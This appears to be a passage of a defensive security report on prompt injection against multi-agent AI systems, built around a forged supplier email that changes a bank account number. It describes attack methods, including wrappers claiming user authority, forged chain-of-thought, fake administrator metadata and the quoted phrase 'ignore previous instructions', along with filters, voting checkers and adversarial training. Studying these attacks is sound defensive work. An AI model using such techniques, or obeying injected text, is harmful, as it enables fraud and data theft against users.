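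Google searched Common Crawl, a public archive of websites, for known patterns of prompt injection. The archive holds 2 to 3 billion pages a month, according to Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild*. SecurityWeek explains that the researchers then used Gemini and human reviewers to remove false positives. Google found that many of the hits were research papers and articles about prompt injection, which made this filtering important.

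The remaining cases included pranks, attempts to keep AI agents away, search engine manipulation and some malicious text. A few injections asked for private files. Slashdot's *Google Studies Prompt Injection Attacks Against AI Agents Browsing the Web* quotes a passage in which Google reports that it did not find significant numbers of advanced attacks and concludes that attackers had not yet used the published research at scale. The scan left out social media and couldn't cover private email, where EchoLeak and ZombieAgent began. A search for known patterns would also miss an email like the one in EchoLeak, which read like a request to a colleague.

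### Whether attacks usually arrive in genuine messages

No published figure measures how often attacks on agents arrive in genuine messages and how often they depend on a false identity. Measuring this would require a representative set of incidents and a record of whether the attacker in each one impersonated somebody, stole a credential or planted text for a genuine agent to read.

Check Point Research's *AI Security Report 2026* (2026) says that detections of longer malicious prompts rose about fivefold between March and May 2026, to nearly 1 percent of the prompts Check Point observed. Check Point treats the rise as a sign of more indirect injection because longer prompts are more typical of attacks that arrive in documents or other content. SmarterArticles incorrectly repeats the figure as a count of indirect injections. The figure counts attempted attacks, whether or not they succeeded,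 and covers only the prompts that Check Point sees.

Surveys don't help much either. Rallies' *Check Point Finds 78% AI Incidents and 51-Point Security Enforcement Gap* reports Check Point's finding that 78 percent of organisations had confirmed or suspected AI-related security incidents in the past year. The figure combines confirmed incidents with suspected ones and doesn't separate injection from stolen credentials.

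Entries in incident databases can be unreliable evidence of real attacks. The OECD, an intergovernmental organisation, runs an incident monitor that uses AI to summarise news reports. Its entry *ZombieAgent Vulnerability Enables Data Theft and Account Takeover in ChatGPT* (2026) states that data thefts occurred before OpenAI's fix, but Radware's own account describes only demonstrations. An earlier OECD entry, *ChatGPT Connectors Vulnerability Enables Zero-Click Data Theft via Poisoned Documents* (2025), begins by describing a researchers' demonstration, then classifies it as exploitation that caused harm. A count of attacks based on such entries would therefore include demonstrations as well as thefts.

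Counting the published cases would be misleading too. Researchers write about new techniques rather than ordinary password thefts, which makes injection look more common among actual attacks than it is. But some victims of a successful injection may never find out, because their logs show an authorised agent doing something it was allowed to do.

Criminals are known to be using kits like Kali365 successfully, while few losses from injection have been confirmed, so stolen credentials have probably caused more harm than injection so far. This is a guess about the present, and it applies more to attacks on companies in general than to attacks on agents. There is even less public evidence about attacks carried in messages between agents. The two documented attacks of this kind, session smuggling and cross-agent escalation, are both demonstrations, and only cross-agent escalation involves a genuine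 agent that was deceived into passing the attack on.

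## Which established security principles carry over to agents

Companies have to protect their agents whatever the incident data eventually shows, and most will start with principles older than language models. Each principle depends on an assumption about the system it protects. We can test whether agents meet that assumption by supposing that the attacker's email has already fooled the Reader's model, and perhaps the model in Payments too. Only some of the principles still prevent harm in that case.

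### Principles that don't rely on the agent's judgement

Saltzer and Schroeder (1975), in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, set out eight design principles for shared computers, which they offered as warnings rather than absolute rules. An intruder on those computers could be a legitimate user. An agent poses a similar problem when it uses its own valid credentials to follow instructions in a stranger's email. Three of the eight principles matter most here.

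Least privilege means giving every program and user only the privileges their job requires. Its main benefit is limiting the damage from an accident or error. It requires someone to list what the job needs and something outside the program to enforce that list. Enforcement is no harder for agents than for other programs. The Reader doesn't have permission to send money, so it can't, even if the email completely fools its model. Writing the list is harder for agents because people often give them jobs whose steps nobody can predict. A general assistant might need access to a travel account one day and a code repository the next, so it needs either broad permissions or, as a later section describes, new ones for each task.

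Complete mediation means checking every access to every object. It works only if the program cannot bypass the check. Agents largely meet this condition because a model can only produce text, and the surrounding program decides whether to run any tool call in that text. The exception is an agent that can run its own code. A single approved call might then open thousands of files, and only the operating system can check each of them.

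Saltzer and Schroeder add that complete mediation requires a foolproof way to identify the source of every request. Payments can identify the Reader, but not the stranger whose email led to the request.

Separation of privilege means requiring two keys, held by different people or programs, as banks do for safe-deposit boxes. With the keys held separately, Saltzer and Schroeder write, "no single accident, deception, or breach of trust is sufficient" to compromise the information. The principle is especially relevant to agents because it covers deception, but it assumes that the same trick won't work on both key holders. If a second agent approves the change of account after reading the Reader's summary, the attacker has obtained both keys with one email. If the second key belongs to a clerk who phones Harlow Paper on a number the company already had, the attacker has to deceive Harlow or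 the clerk as well.

The Australian Signals Directorate and its partner agencies recommend a related separation of duties, with roles such as "Orchestrator", "Reader" and "Actuator". The company in the example already separates its agents this way, but that doesn't prevent Payments from accepting the Reader's messages as true.

Segmentation, another established practice, divides a system into parts with few connections between them, so that a break-in doesn't spread. In the agencies' hypothetical case of the customer support agent, poor segmentation lets the attacker move on to neighbouring agents that handle billing and refunds. Segmentation depends on the company knowing all the connections, but agents that share a folder or a memory have a connection that may not appear on any network diagram. Saltzer and Schroeder also advised designers to minimise shared mechanisms, because each is a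 potential path for information between users.

The company needs the connection between the Reader and Payments, so segmentation can't remove it but can reduce how many agents an injected request reaches afterwards. In the experiments by Papadopoulos and colleagues, harmful content usually stopped at the first hop when the infected agent could message only one other agent.

Audit logging also carries over to agents. Saltzer and Schroeder compared this approach to putting an unbreakable padlock on a flimsy file cabinet, which a thief can break into but not without leaving visible damage. They noted that computer systems rarely relied on it because a clever attacker could erase the evidence. An agent must therefore be unable to change or delete its own log. The agencies recommend running agents in enclaves without write access to logs, and holding any request to delete a log until a human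 has reviewed it.

The contents of the log matter as much as its protection. A log that recorded only who changed which record would make the Payments attack look legitimate, as the logs did in the agencies' procurement example. The agencies also recommend recording what information an agent retrieved, and David C of the UK's National Cyber Security Centre suggests keeping the model's full input and output. With those records, an investigator could trace account number 4471 back to the email. The money might be gone by then, so a log can only complement the other principles.

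### Attestation

Attestation is evidence about what a machine is running, such as the program hash that SPIRE can check before it gives the Reader a certificate. Relying on it means assuming that a program's code determines its behaviour, but the Reader's behaviour also depends on what it has read. Code attestation still detects when an attacker replaces the program, so it carries over in part.

Li, Niu and colleagues (2026), in *Attestation is All You Need*, try to extend attestation from code to behaviour. They study high-performance computing centres, where many research groups share the same machines and storage. Their main concern is what they call the hijacked authorised agent. A researcher starts an agent, which inherits the researcher's login and file permissions. The agent then reads an instruction that an attacker has hidden in the header of a data file or left in a temporary folder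 shared by jobs on the same machine. Authentication and authorisation both succeed. The centre has to allow the agent's encrypted connection to the company that runs its model, so the agent can send data out through that connection.

Their system, AEGIS, works in five steps:

1. Before a job starts, an administrator or user approves a profile of the files, network addresses, tools and amounts of data that the task needs. AEGIS ties the profile to the job.
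2. A probe in the operating system records the files the agent opens, the connections it makes and the programs it starts.
3. Every second, AEGIS signs this record and sends it to a central verifier.
4. The verifier compares the record with the profile. It also looks for cases where one agent writes a file and another soon reads it, which may indicate a hidden channel.
5. If the agent has broken a rule, AEGIS slows it down, cuts off its file access, or suspends or ends the job.

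Li and colleagues ran four kinds of attack three times each, and AEGIS detected all of them, typically within half a second. Between 50 and 519 bytes leaked before detection, depending on the attack. That is a tiny fraction of a genomics dataset, but it is enough to contain a whole password or bank account number. AEGIS raised no false alarms in 42 harmless actions.

These are small tests, and the researchers wrote the attacks themselves. In a controlled version, AEGIS missed one of the four attacks when they turned off its matching of known injection patterns. They acknowledge that the protection depends on the quality of the profile. A tight profile seems feasible for a supercomputer job that reads one project's files and never touches another's. But a profile for Payments would have to allow changes to suppliers' bank details, so AEGIS would not flag the change to Harlow's.

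### Anomaly detection and reputation

Anomaly detection assumes that an attack looks different from normal work. Li and colleagues compared AEGIS with several conventional defences. The one that analysed each agent's behaviour separately missed all four attacks, while network monitoring, file auditing and strict sandboxing each caught two. Each agent's behaviour looked plausible on its own, and the attack that two agents carried out together was visible only in their combined records.

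Attackers may be easier to detect while they are still working out what to write. David C expects them to need several attempts and recommends watching for failed tool calls. Data from a public competition supports the expectation that most attempts fail. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports about 272,000 attempts against 13 models, of which 8,648 succeeded. Even the most vulnerable model resisted more than nine attempts in ten. But a careful attacker can practise on their own account with the same model and send the victim only the version that works, so anomaly detection works better against careless attackers.

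Reputation systems assume that past conduct predicts future conduct. The agencies recommend giving agents trust scores and lowering them after anomalous behaviour. Lowering the score makes sense when the cause persists, as when an agent has saved an attacker's instructions to its memory. A high score is much weaker evidence of future conduct. If the Reader has sent 1,000 honest summaries, the company knows that it handles ordinary mail well, but the attacker wrote the email to get a different result. The Reader's record would still be just as good right before it passed on the false account number.

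A company might do better to score the outside sources its agents read. Payments could give more weight to an address Harlow has used for five years than to one that first appeared this morning. To do that, Payments would need to know which address the claim came from.

### Input sanitisation and the comparison with SQL injection

Sanitisation means removing or neutralising the dangerous parts of an input before a program uses it. It assumes that a developer can identify those parts. For databases there is an even better method, the parameterised query, which makes it unnecessary to look for dangerous parts at all. A query to update a supplier's account might look like this:

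```sql
UPDATE suppliers SET account = ? WHERE name = ?
```

If an attacker enters a command as the value for the first question mark, the database just stores it as odd-looking text. David C also gives a hardware example, where some ARM processors tag regions of memory with their purpose and enforce the separation.

David C argues that a language model has nothing corresponding to the question mark. Developers can train a model to prioritize instructions over data, mark which text is data, or try to detect injections, but these methods all add a distinction between instructions and data that the underlying technology doesn't make. He therefore proposes treating prompt injection as the exploitation of an "inherently confusable deputy". Tymshare could repair Hardy's compiler by changing how it received authority to write files. David C argues that no comparable repair removes the risk from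 a model, so designers should make attacks less likely and limit the harm with safeguards outside the model. If the remaining risk is too high, the task may be a poor use of a language model.

This argument is convincing for current models, but models that take in instructions and data as separate streams might eventually weaken it.

But even a perfect separation would not have protected Payments. Suppose its tool updates the database with the query above. The database correctly treats the value 4471 as data and stores it as the account number, so the supplier's record is now wrong. Parameterised queries prevent a value from acting as a command, but they don't check whether it is true. The comparison with SQL injection is therefore misleading in another way, because some attacks on agents require only a false statement.

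Sanitisation is still worth doing. A server can encode forged role markers as ordinary text, as in the tests by Zhan and colleagues. A mail program can remove white text on a white background before it reaches the Reader, and Payments can refuse an account number that contains letters. These checks work because a developer can define the formats exactly, but an attacker's account number in the right format would still pass.

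David C compares prompt injection to SQL injection, which people were exploiting in the 1990s. SQL injection attacks peaked only around 2010, and it took years of breaches to get safer defaults. He fears a similar wave of attacks if companies add language models to most of their applications without designing for prompt injection.

### Allow-lists and known attack strings

An allow-list names the tools, addresses or senders that a system accepts. It carries over well as a limit on what an agent can reach. Saltzer and Schroeder preferred allow-lists to lists of forbidden things because users soon complain when a legitimate action is missing from the list, while nobody may notice that a harmful action was never forbidden.

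It is a mistake to treat a party's place on an allowlist as evidence that the content is safe, because that party may not control everything that passes through it. In EchoLeak, the stolen data left through an approved Microsoft Teams service. The hijacked agents that Li and colleagues describe use an approved connection to the model provider. In the Payments example, the Reader is a permitted sender, but that does not establish who wrote the emails it summarises.

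Matching known attack strings fails because an attack doesn't have to contain a recognisable sequence of characters. Blocking the phrase "ignore previous instructions" stops only attackers who use that phrase, and David C points out that there are endless ways to reword it.

The competition data gives some idea of how varied successful attacks are. Dziemian and colleagues searched 2,679 of them for groups of near-copies that worked in at least three scenarios. They found five groups, with 117 attacks in total, or about 4 percent. The largest group, which told the model that it was in a simulation with a control panel, worked in 21 of the 41 scenarios. Blocking these five templates would be worthwhile but would not stop most of the attacks, although filters for narrower groups would catch some more.

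Lists of dangerous actions have similar gaps. Yang (2026), in *Evaluate the Stack, Not the Layer*, tested a list of 50 patterns on actions that agents might propose. The list missed 85.7 percent of the actions it should have blocked, even though nobody was trying to evade it. A larger set of 174 rules did much better overall, but missed 52.9 percent in areas it hadn't been written for. The Harlow message contains no known attack string, just an ordinary sentence about a bank account.

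### Redundancy and consensus

The agencies recommend requiring approval from several agents for moderate-stakes actions and adding human approval for high-stakes ones. They also suggest using redundant agents to validate each other's outputs. But they also warn that a compromised agent can exploit consensus mechanisms. Whether consensus helps depends mostly on whether the agents make the same mistakes.

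The theory behind this is Byzantine agreement, which Pease, Shostak and Lamport developed in the early 1980s. A group has to agree even though some members are faulty and may do anything, including telling different members different things. In the basic version, where messages carry no signatures, a group needs at least 3f + 1 members to tolerate f faulty ones, so tolerating one faulty member takes at least four members.

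Three agents are too few to reach agreement reliably if one of them may lie. Suppose agents A, B and C must agree on whether to make a payment. B tells A to pay, but C reports that B told it to refuse. Either B gave two different answers or C is lying about what B said, and A cannot tell which. With a fourth agent, A can compare more reports and follow the majority.

Zanolini (2026) explains in *Correlated Failures of AI Approval Monitors* that the requirement drops to 2f + 1 when the question has a factual answer and every checker sees the same request. Three checkers can then tolerate one that is wrong about a bank account. But both formulas hold only if at most f checkers are wrong, so three checkers offer no protection when a single email fools two of them.

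Engineers often justify a small f by assuming that members fail independently. If three checkers each err with probability p, a majority is wrong when two or three of them err:

$$P_{\text{ind}} = 3p^2(1-p) + p^3$$

With p at 10 percent, this gives 2.8 percent, a large improvement on a single checker. If all three share one weakness and always err together, the rate stays at 10 percent. Real checkers will be somewhere in between. In a simple model, the three act as one checker in a share c of cases and err independently in the rest:

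$$P = c\,p + (1-c)\,P_{\text{ind}}$$

Here c is also the correlation between the errors of any two checkers.

| Correlation between checkers' errors | Wrong majority when each errs 10% of the time |
| --- | --- |
| 0 | 2.8% |
| 0.4 | 5.7% |
| 1 | 10% |

The 10 percent figure also depends on the cases being ordinary. An attacker chooses a case that the checkers are likely to get wrong, and voting then makes an error more likely. If a forged email fools each checker 70 percent of the time, the majority of three independent checkers will be wrong 78 percent of the time. Some of the forgeries that Wang and Mannby tested fooled strong models almost every time.

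### How correlated the errors of language models are

A good deal of evidence suggests that different models make the same mistakes. In *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models*, Kim, Garg and colleagues (2025) compared 71 models on more than 14,000 multiple-choice questions. When two models both got a question wrong, they chose the same wrong answer about 60 percent of the time, compared with the 33 percent expected by chance. Models from the same company agreed more often, but so did more accurate models from different companies. Buying the best model from each of three companies may therefore provide less diversity than expected.

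A majority vote can be less accurate than the best single model. In *Do Large Language Models Know Colombian Law?* (2026), a majority vote of 15 models was right on 84.3 percent of the questions, while the best single model was right on 90.5 percent. At least one model had the right answer to 98.4 percent of the questions, but the majority vote did not always select it.

Kohli (2026), in *Nine Judges, Two Effective Votes*, measured how much independent information a panel contains. Nine models from seven families judged, among other things, whether one sentence followed from another. For k judges whose errors have an average correlation of φ, the number of effective votes is

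$$n_{\text{eff}} = \frac{k}{1 + (k-1)\,\varphi}$$

On the main dataset, the correlation φ was 0.391, so the nine judges were equivalent to about 2.2 independent ones. Adding more judges with the same correlation would never raise that figure above 2.6. Even when all nine agreed, they were wrong about 9 percent of the time. The questions were often ambiguous, and Kohli used the majority view of 100 people as the right answer, so judges might do better on a check with a clear answer.

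Yang tested something closer to the agencies' recommendation, with models deciding whether to block an agent's proposed action. Two of the models each missed 10.5 percent of the harmful actions. If their errors had been independent, 1.1 percent would have got past both, but 5.2 percent did. Pairing one of these models with the 174 fixed rules let only 1.3 percent through, even though the rules alone missed 13.4 percent. A less accurate second checker can therefore be more useful than a better one if it fails for different reasons than the first. Part of the overlap between the models may just reflect actions that were hard to judge, and the test did not include an attacker who adapted to the checks.

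Under deliberate attack, models share weaknesses too. Dziemian and colleagues took the 44 attacks in their sample that had beaten Claude Opus 4.5, the most robust model in the competition, and tried them on the other models. They worked 44 to 81 percent of the time, depending on the model. Attacks that had beaten a weak model rarely worked on a strong one, and none of those that had beaten Qwen3 VL worked on Opus. If one strong model and two weak ones decide by majority vote, an attacker can win by fooling only the weak ones, and the company would be safer with the strong model alone. Requiring unanimous approval avoids this, but then any one checker can block a legitimate payment.

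Voting among models protects somewhat better against injections when the models come from different families. *Evaluating and Improving the Robustness of Large Language Models* (2026) reports preliminary experiments in which voting was substantially less effective at reducing the success of injections when all the models came from one family.

### Whether agents can follow an agreement protocol

Agents can also fail to agree when none of them is faulty. In *Can AI Agents Agree?*, Berdoz, Rugli and Wattenhofer (2026) had groups of agents exchange proposals to try to settle on a number that one of them had started with. The agents had no reason to prefer any number, but only 41.6 percent of the runs without a faulty agent ended in valid agreement. Larger groups did worse. With the better of the two models tested, just mentioning in the prompt that some agents might be malicious reduced the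 rate from 75.4 to 59.1 percent.

When Berdoz and colleagues added malicious agents, the group usually ran out of time and seldom settled on a bad value. For Payments, that would mean a late payment rather than a stolen one. The models were small, with 8 and 14 billion parameters, so stronger ones may well do better. A company can also avoid the problem by having ordinary software collect and count the votes.

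*A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (2026) concludes that classical fault-tolerance guarantees don't apply to agents. It argues that the theory assumes deterministic, verifiable behaviour and a fixed, known number of faulty members, whereas agents are unpredictable and an infection can spread, so the number of faulty agents can grow. The spread of infection is the stronger objection. Unpredictability matters less because the theory already allows faulty members to do anything, so an agent that errs can count as faulty.

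Some results are more encouraging. *Robust Multi-Agent LLMs under Byzantine Faults* (2026) reports a method that preserves the honest agents' abilities, even though an agent cannot tell trustworthy messages from malicious ones by itself. *Rethinking the Reliability of Multi-agent System* (2025) found that language-model agents were more sceptical of erroneous messages than traditional agents. Its method, which gives more weight to confident agents, performed well even when 85.7 percent of the agents were faulty.

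That is far beyond the classical limit, and it is possible because the method uses the models' own ability to recognise a wrong answer. This can work when an agent can answer the question itself. But Payments could not work out Harlow's account number by reasoning, and a more confident agent would be no more likely to know it.

For facts of this kind, the company needs more sources of evidence rather than more agents reading the same evidence. Three agents that all read the Reader's summary depend on one email, so Zanolini recommends counting sources instead of votes. One checker could read the original email, another could consult the company's existing record of Harlow, and a person could phone. The agencies' guidance also recommends confirming critical details against multiple sources. That recommendation deserves more weight than their advice on redundant agents.

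### The principles compared

| Principle | What it assumes | Whether agents meet the assumption | Carries over |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Least privilege | Someone can list what the job needs, and software outside the agent enforces it | Yes, though the list is hard to write for open-ended jobs | Largely |
| Complete mediation | The program cannot get around the check | Yes, if the check also covers code the agent runs | Largely |
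| Separation of privilege | One deception won't obtain both keys | Yes, if the key holders rely on different evidence | Largely |
| Segmentation | The company knows every connection | Yes, if it counts shared files and memory | Largely |
| Audit logs | The log is complete and the attacker cannot change it | Yes, if software outside the agent also records what the agent read | Largely |
| Attestation | Code determines behaviour | No, but it still detects a modified program | In part |
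| Anomaly detection | Attacks look unusual | Sometimes | In part |
| Reputation | Past conduct predicts future conduct | For ordinary inputs, but not for an attacker's | In part |
| Input sanitisation | A developer can define the dangerous parts | For markers and formats, but not for meaning | In part |
| Redundancy | Checkers rarely fail together | Rarely, if they are similar models reading the same evidence | In part |
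| Allow-list membership as evidence of safe content | A listed party controls what passes through it | No | No |
| Matching known attack strings | An attack needs particular wording | No | No |

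## Judging the text with filters and trained resistance

A list of forbidden phrases misses any attack that uses other words, but a language model can respond to what a sentence means. Developers can have a separate model scan messages for attacks before the agent reads them, or train the agent's own model to ignore attacks. Either way, they rely on a model's judgement, so they need to know how often it is wrong.

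### Filters and false alarms

The usual filter is a classifier, a model that scores how likely each message is to contain an attack. The company chooses a threshold and blocks or reviews every message that scores above it. A lower threshold catches more attacks but also flags more messages that contain no attack.

Suppose that 1 message in 1,000 is harmful, and that a filter catches 99 percent of harmful messages and wrongly flags 1 percent of harmless ones. Of 100,000 messages, 100 are harmful, and the filter flags 99 of them. It also flags 999 of the 99,900 harmless messages. That makes 1,098 alarms, or about eleven for each attack it catches. The chance that a flagged message is harmful is therefore only about 9 percent:

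$$P(\text{harmful} \mid \text{flagged}) = \frac{0.99 \times 0.001}{0.99 \times 0.001 + 0.01 \times 0.999} \approx 0.09$$

The same filter looks much better or worse depending on how common attacks are.

| Harmful messages | Alarms per attack caught | Share of alarms that are real |
| --- | --- | --- |
| 1 in 100 | 2 | 50% |
| 1 in 1,000 | 11 | 9% |
| 1 in 10,000 | 102 | 1% |

If 1 in 1,000 messages is an attack, a company that handles 2,000 messages a day would get about 22 alarms a day, 20 of them false. If it blocks every flagged message, it will lose some honest requests from suppliers. If a clerk reviews them instead, he or she will see ten harmless messages for every attack and may start approving them by reflex. Cutting the false alarm rate from 1 percent to 0.1 percent would make about half of the alarms real. Raising the catch rate from 99 to 99.9 percent would hardly change the number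 of alarms, but it would reduce missed attacks from one every 50 days to one every 500.

These figures also assume that attackers don't adapt to the filter, but Aim Labs did in EchoLeak. The company should at least put its filter in front of the Reader, where the email's odd address and hidden text are still visible. A filter between the two agents would receive only the Reader's two ordinary sentences.

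### Marking untrusted passages

A developer can also leave the text in place and mark it as untrusted. The simplest way is to put a delimiter before and after each email and tell the model not to obey any instructions in between. An attacker who knows the delimiter can type it in the email to make the untrusted part seem to end early, so the software should generate a new random delimiter for each email.

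Ye and colleagues describe other defences that mark the source throughout the passage. For example, software might replace every space in the email with an unusual character, and the system prompt might explain that text in this form is only data. The attacker can't remove these marks, because the software adds them after the email arrives. Marking is easy to add and doesn't require retraining the model, but its effect still depends on how much weight the model gives the marks.

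Attackers can send competing signals. Ye and colleagues put the same command to upload a secret file inside 212 different wrappers and hid them in web pages. They ranked the wrappers by how strongly the model's internal activity registered the command as user text. Wrappers that declared that the text came from the user made up 24 percent of the total but all of the top 5 percent. In 1,000 attempts, the attack succeeded 2 percent of the time where the signal was weakest and 70 percent where it was strongest.

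An even more effective disguise imitated the model's chain of thought, the reasoning it writes before it answers. An ordinary hidden command almost never worked on most of the models, but with forged reasoning added, it worked 56 to 70 percent of the time on all of them. In a related chat experiment, absurd reasons worked about as well as plausible ones, but rewriting the forgery in a different style cut its success rate from 61 to 10 percent. The models seem to have accepted the forgery because it sounded like their own reasoning, regardless of what it argued.

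### The instruction hierarchy

Developers also train models to give different sources different authority. OpenAI researchers proposed this method, the instruction hierarchy, in 2024. *Training LLMs to Enforce Multi-Level Instruction Hierarchies via Gravity-Weighted Direct Preference Optimization* (2026) gives a precise version with five levels, from highest to lowest:

- $L_0$: the platform's rules
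- $L_1$: the developer's system prompt
- $L_2$: settings for the individual user
- $L_3$: the user's message
- $L_4$: data and tool outputs

If instructions at two levels conflict, the model must follow the higher one. If they are compatible, it must follow both.

If the Reader applied the rule about compatible instructions literally, it would follow the hidden instruction in the Harlow email to include the new account number in any summary. Maria asked for a summary, and nothing in her request rules out including the number.

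OpenAI's Model Spec, its public description of how its models should behave, is stricter than Anthropic's ranking for Claude, which Anthropic says is not a strict one. *When Context Gets Root* (2026) describes the Model Spec as giving tool outputs no authority to issue instructions by default. Under that rule, the Reader should ignore the request to mention the number. But the Reader might well include the number, because a good summary of an email about a new bank account includes the account number.

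Even the strict rule requires the model to recognise an instruction. *Where Instruction Hierarchy Breaks* (2026) argues that whether a message is an instruction or data depends on context, since the same tool output can be harmless information in one setting and imply an order in another.

The instruction hierarchy works like an access control list inside the model, because a text's authority depends on who supplied it. Software outside the model can verify a sender with a cryptographic key, but the model can only infer the sender from labels and style, which attackers can imitate.

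OpenAI saw this happen with an AI agent that ran a vending machine in its office. An automated attacker got the agent to cut an expensive item's price to $0.50 by adding fake metadata that made its message appear to come from a trusted administrator. An ordinary identity check would have helped if software had compared the sender's verified account with a list of administrators before allowing the change. It wouldn't help Payments, because the label naming the Reader is correct.

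### Where a peer agent's message should rank

*When Context Gets Root* lists other agents among the sources that need a level, but the five-level hierarchy has no separate level for them. If Payments treats the Reader's messages as user messages, a request injected into them gains the user's authority. If it treats them as tool output with no authority, it won't act on even the Reader's legitimate requests.

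A reasonable compromise is to present the message as data and have the developer's system prompt list the requests that Payments may act on. The prompt might allow Payments to record invoices that the Reader reports but forbid it to change bank details based on a summary. The authority for each action then comes from the developer, and the Reader supplies only the details. This should make it harder for an injected request to trigger an action that isn't on the list, although a false invoice could still get through.

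Another option is to add more priority levels. In *Many-Tier Instruction Hierarchy in LLM Agents*, Zhang, Li and colleagues (2026) put a numbered tag around each instruction and tell the model that lower numbers take priority. The agent's software can assign these numbers by source. A tag can also cover part of a message, so the Reader's own words could have rank 5 and a quotation from an email rank 12.

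The test covered 853 tasks. In the coding tasks, a model writes a Python function while following 12 style instructions, many of which contradict each other and which are ranked on up to 12 levels. Frontier models such as GPT-5.4 passed only about 40 percent of the 853 tasks, and scores fell as the number of levels rose. Changing only the format of the tags lowered the scores of GPT-5.4 and Claude Opus 4.6 by more than 8 percent.

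The low scores are partly due to strict scoring. A coding task has an average of six instructions that should take priority, and the model passes only if it follows all of them and writes working code. A model that handled each instruction correctly 86 percent of the time would pass about 40 percent of such tasks. Newer models may do better. But none of the conflicts were disguised, whereas an attacker would disguise them.

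Zhang and colleagues assume that the software already has the rank of each instruction. The software at Payments couldn't give the sentence about the account number a lower rank, because the Reader's summary leaves out that sentence's source.

### Training against an automated attacker

Adversarial training exposes a model to attacks and rewards it for resisting them. It needs many varied attacks, because a model trained on a small collection learns to resist those patterns but stays vulnerable to others.

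OpenAI has trained other models to supply attacks. *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes an automated attacker that targeted the company's browser agent. In one simulation, a user asked the agent to write an out-of-office reply, but the agent came across a planted email and sent the user's resignation to the chief executive instead. OpenAI trained the agent against such attacks and released the new version to all users.

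GPT-Red, from July 2026, applies the method on a much larger scale. Wallace, Choquette-Choo and colleagues (2026), in *GPT-Red*, describe how the attacker trains together with several defenders, the models it attacks:

1. The training program picks a defender and a task, such as answering a question from search results.
2. It picks a place where an outsider could plausibly add text, such as one search result or the body of an email, and gives the attacker a goal, such as stealing a key.
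3. The attacker writes an injection, tries it on the defender, looks at what happened and revises it.
4. The attacker submits a final version. Automatic checks reject it if it breaks the rules, for example by changing something an outsider couldn't reach.
5. The defender does the task with the injection in place. The attacker earns a reward if the injection works, and the defender earns one for resisting it and completing the task.
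6. Reinforcement learning adjusts both models to earn more reward, and the cycle repeats.

Rewarding the defender for finishing the task matters because a model that refused everything would be very secure but useless. The attacker tended to settle on a narrow set of tricks against a single defender, but with many defenders it had to look for the weaknesses of each. The training used about as much computing power as the reinforcement learning for OpenAI's recent production models.

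OpenAI then used GPT-Red's attacks to train GPT-5.6. On the company's hardest benchmark for direct injection, GPT-5.6 Sol failed one-sixth as often as OpenAI's best production model from four months before, which is the drop mentioned earlier. GPT-Red had also discovered the forged-reasoning attack independently. According to OpenAI's announcement, *GPT-Red* (2026), such attacks succeeded more than 95 percent of the time on GPT-5.1 and less than 10 percent of the time on GPT-5.6 Sol.

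One published example resembles the Harlow case. A user asks for an agenda for a youth flag-football camp, and a search result contains forged reasoning about including a bank account for the registration fees. GPT-5.1 put the account number in the agenda, while GPT-5.6 identified the text as an injection and ignored it. But a bank account is out of place in search results for football drills, whereas it is normal in an email from a supplier.

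OpenAI also compared GPT-Red with human testers, using scenarios from the competition that Dziemian and colleagues analysed. GPT-Red found a working attack on GPT-5.1 in 84 percent of the scenarios, and the humans did in 13 percent. Part of the difference comes from being able to test attacks on the defender. GPT-5.5, which had no special training as an attacker, did about as well as the humans when it couldn't do this, and much better when it could. Wallace and colleagues point out that humans may find new kinds of attack that GPT-Red would miss.

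### AgentDojo and the trouble with fixed attacks

Researchers commonly test agents with AgentDojo, which Debenedetti and colleagues released in 2024. It gives a single agent 97 tasks and simulated tools for office work, messaging, banking and travel, and plants injections in the data that the tools return. In one banking task, the user asks the agent to pay a bill, and the file with the bill also contains an order to send money to the attacker.

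AgentDojo measures how many tasks the agent completes without an attack, how many it completes under attack, and how often the attacker succeeds. Reporting all three shows when a defence stops attacks only by making the agent useless.

AgentDojo lets researchers add new attacks, but a developer can choose to run only the built-in ones. A good score then shows that a defence stops those attacks, which the developer may have seen while building the defence. A real attacker can study the defence and keep changing the text until something works. Nasr, Carlini and colleagues found in *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025) that adaptive attackers could get past most defences that had looked nearly perfect on fixed tests.

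Later results for GPT-5.6 show how much the choice of test matters:

- On recorded human attacks from the competition, the model resisted every one, after the researchers corrected a grading error.
- When GPT-Red wrote new attacks for the same scenarios and could practise on the model, just under 4 percent of its attempts succeeded.
- On much harder tests, with attacks and scenarios that OpenAI had kept out of training, the model resisted between 50 and 89 percent, though grading errors may have lowered these scores a little.

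Ye and colleagues argue that models resist injections mostly by memorising known attacks, without recognising who is speaking, so developers will always have to respond to new disguises. GPT-5.6 improved on attacks it had never seen, which is evidence that training taught it more than how to recognise specific attacks. But its much lower scores on unseen attacks suggest that a good part of its resistance still depends on familiarity.

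### Current rates of resistance

Developers now publish injection results in system cards, the safety reports that accompany new models. The table gives some results from 2026.

| Model | Test | Attacks that succeeded |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Coding, 200 attempts | 0% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Operating a graphical interface, one attempt | 17.8% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | Operating a browser, per attempt | 31.5%, or 0.5% with added safeguards |
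| GPT-5.6 Sol | Direct injection | 0.05% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | Indirect injection | 3.77% |
| GPT-6 Sol | Direct injection | 0.01% |
| GPT-6 Sol | Indirect injection | 2.87% |

The Opus 4.6 figures come from VentureBeat, and the Opus 4.8 figures come from its article *Anthropic’s browser agent got hijacked 31.5% of the time before safeguards engaged*. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* gives the GPT-5.6 rates and notes that they don't measure how likely a breach is in real use. *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense* (Cross, 2026) reports OpenAI's October results for GPT-6 Sol. The companies use different tests, so readers can't use the table to tell whose model is safer. These are also not the newest models, since OpenAI's *GPT-6.2 System Card* (2026) came out six weeks after the GPT-6 Sol results.

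The indirect rates are the ones that matter for the Reader, and they are far higher than the direct rates. The rates also differ greatly by type of task, as the results for Opus 4.6 show.

A low rate per attempt can still add up if the attacker keeps trying. If each attempt succeeds with probability p and the attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success in n attempts is

$$P(\text{at least one success}) = 1 - (1-p)^n$$

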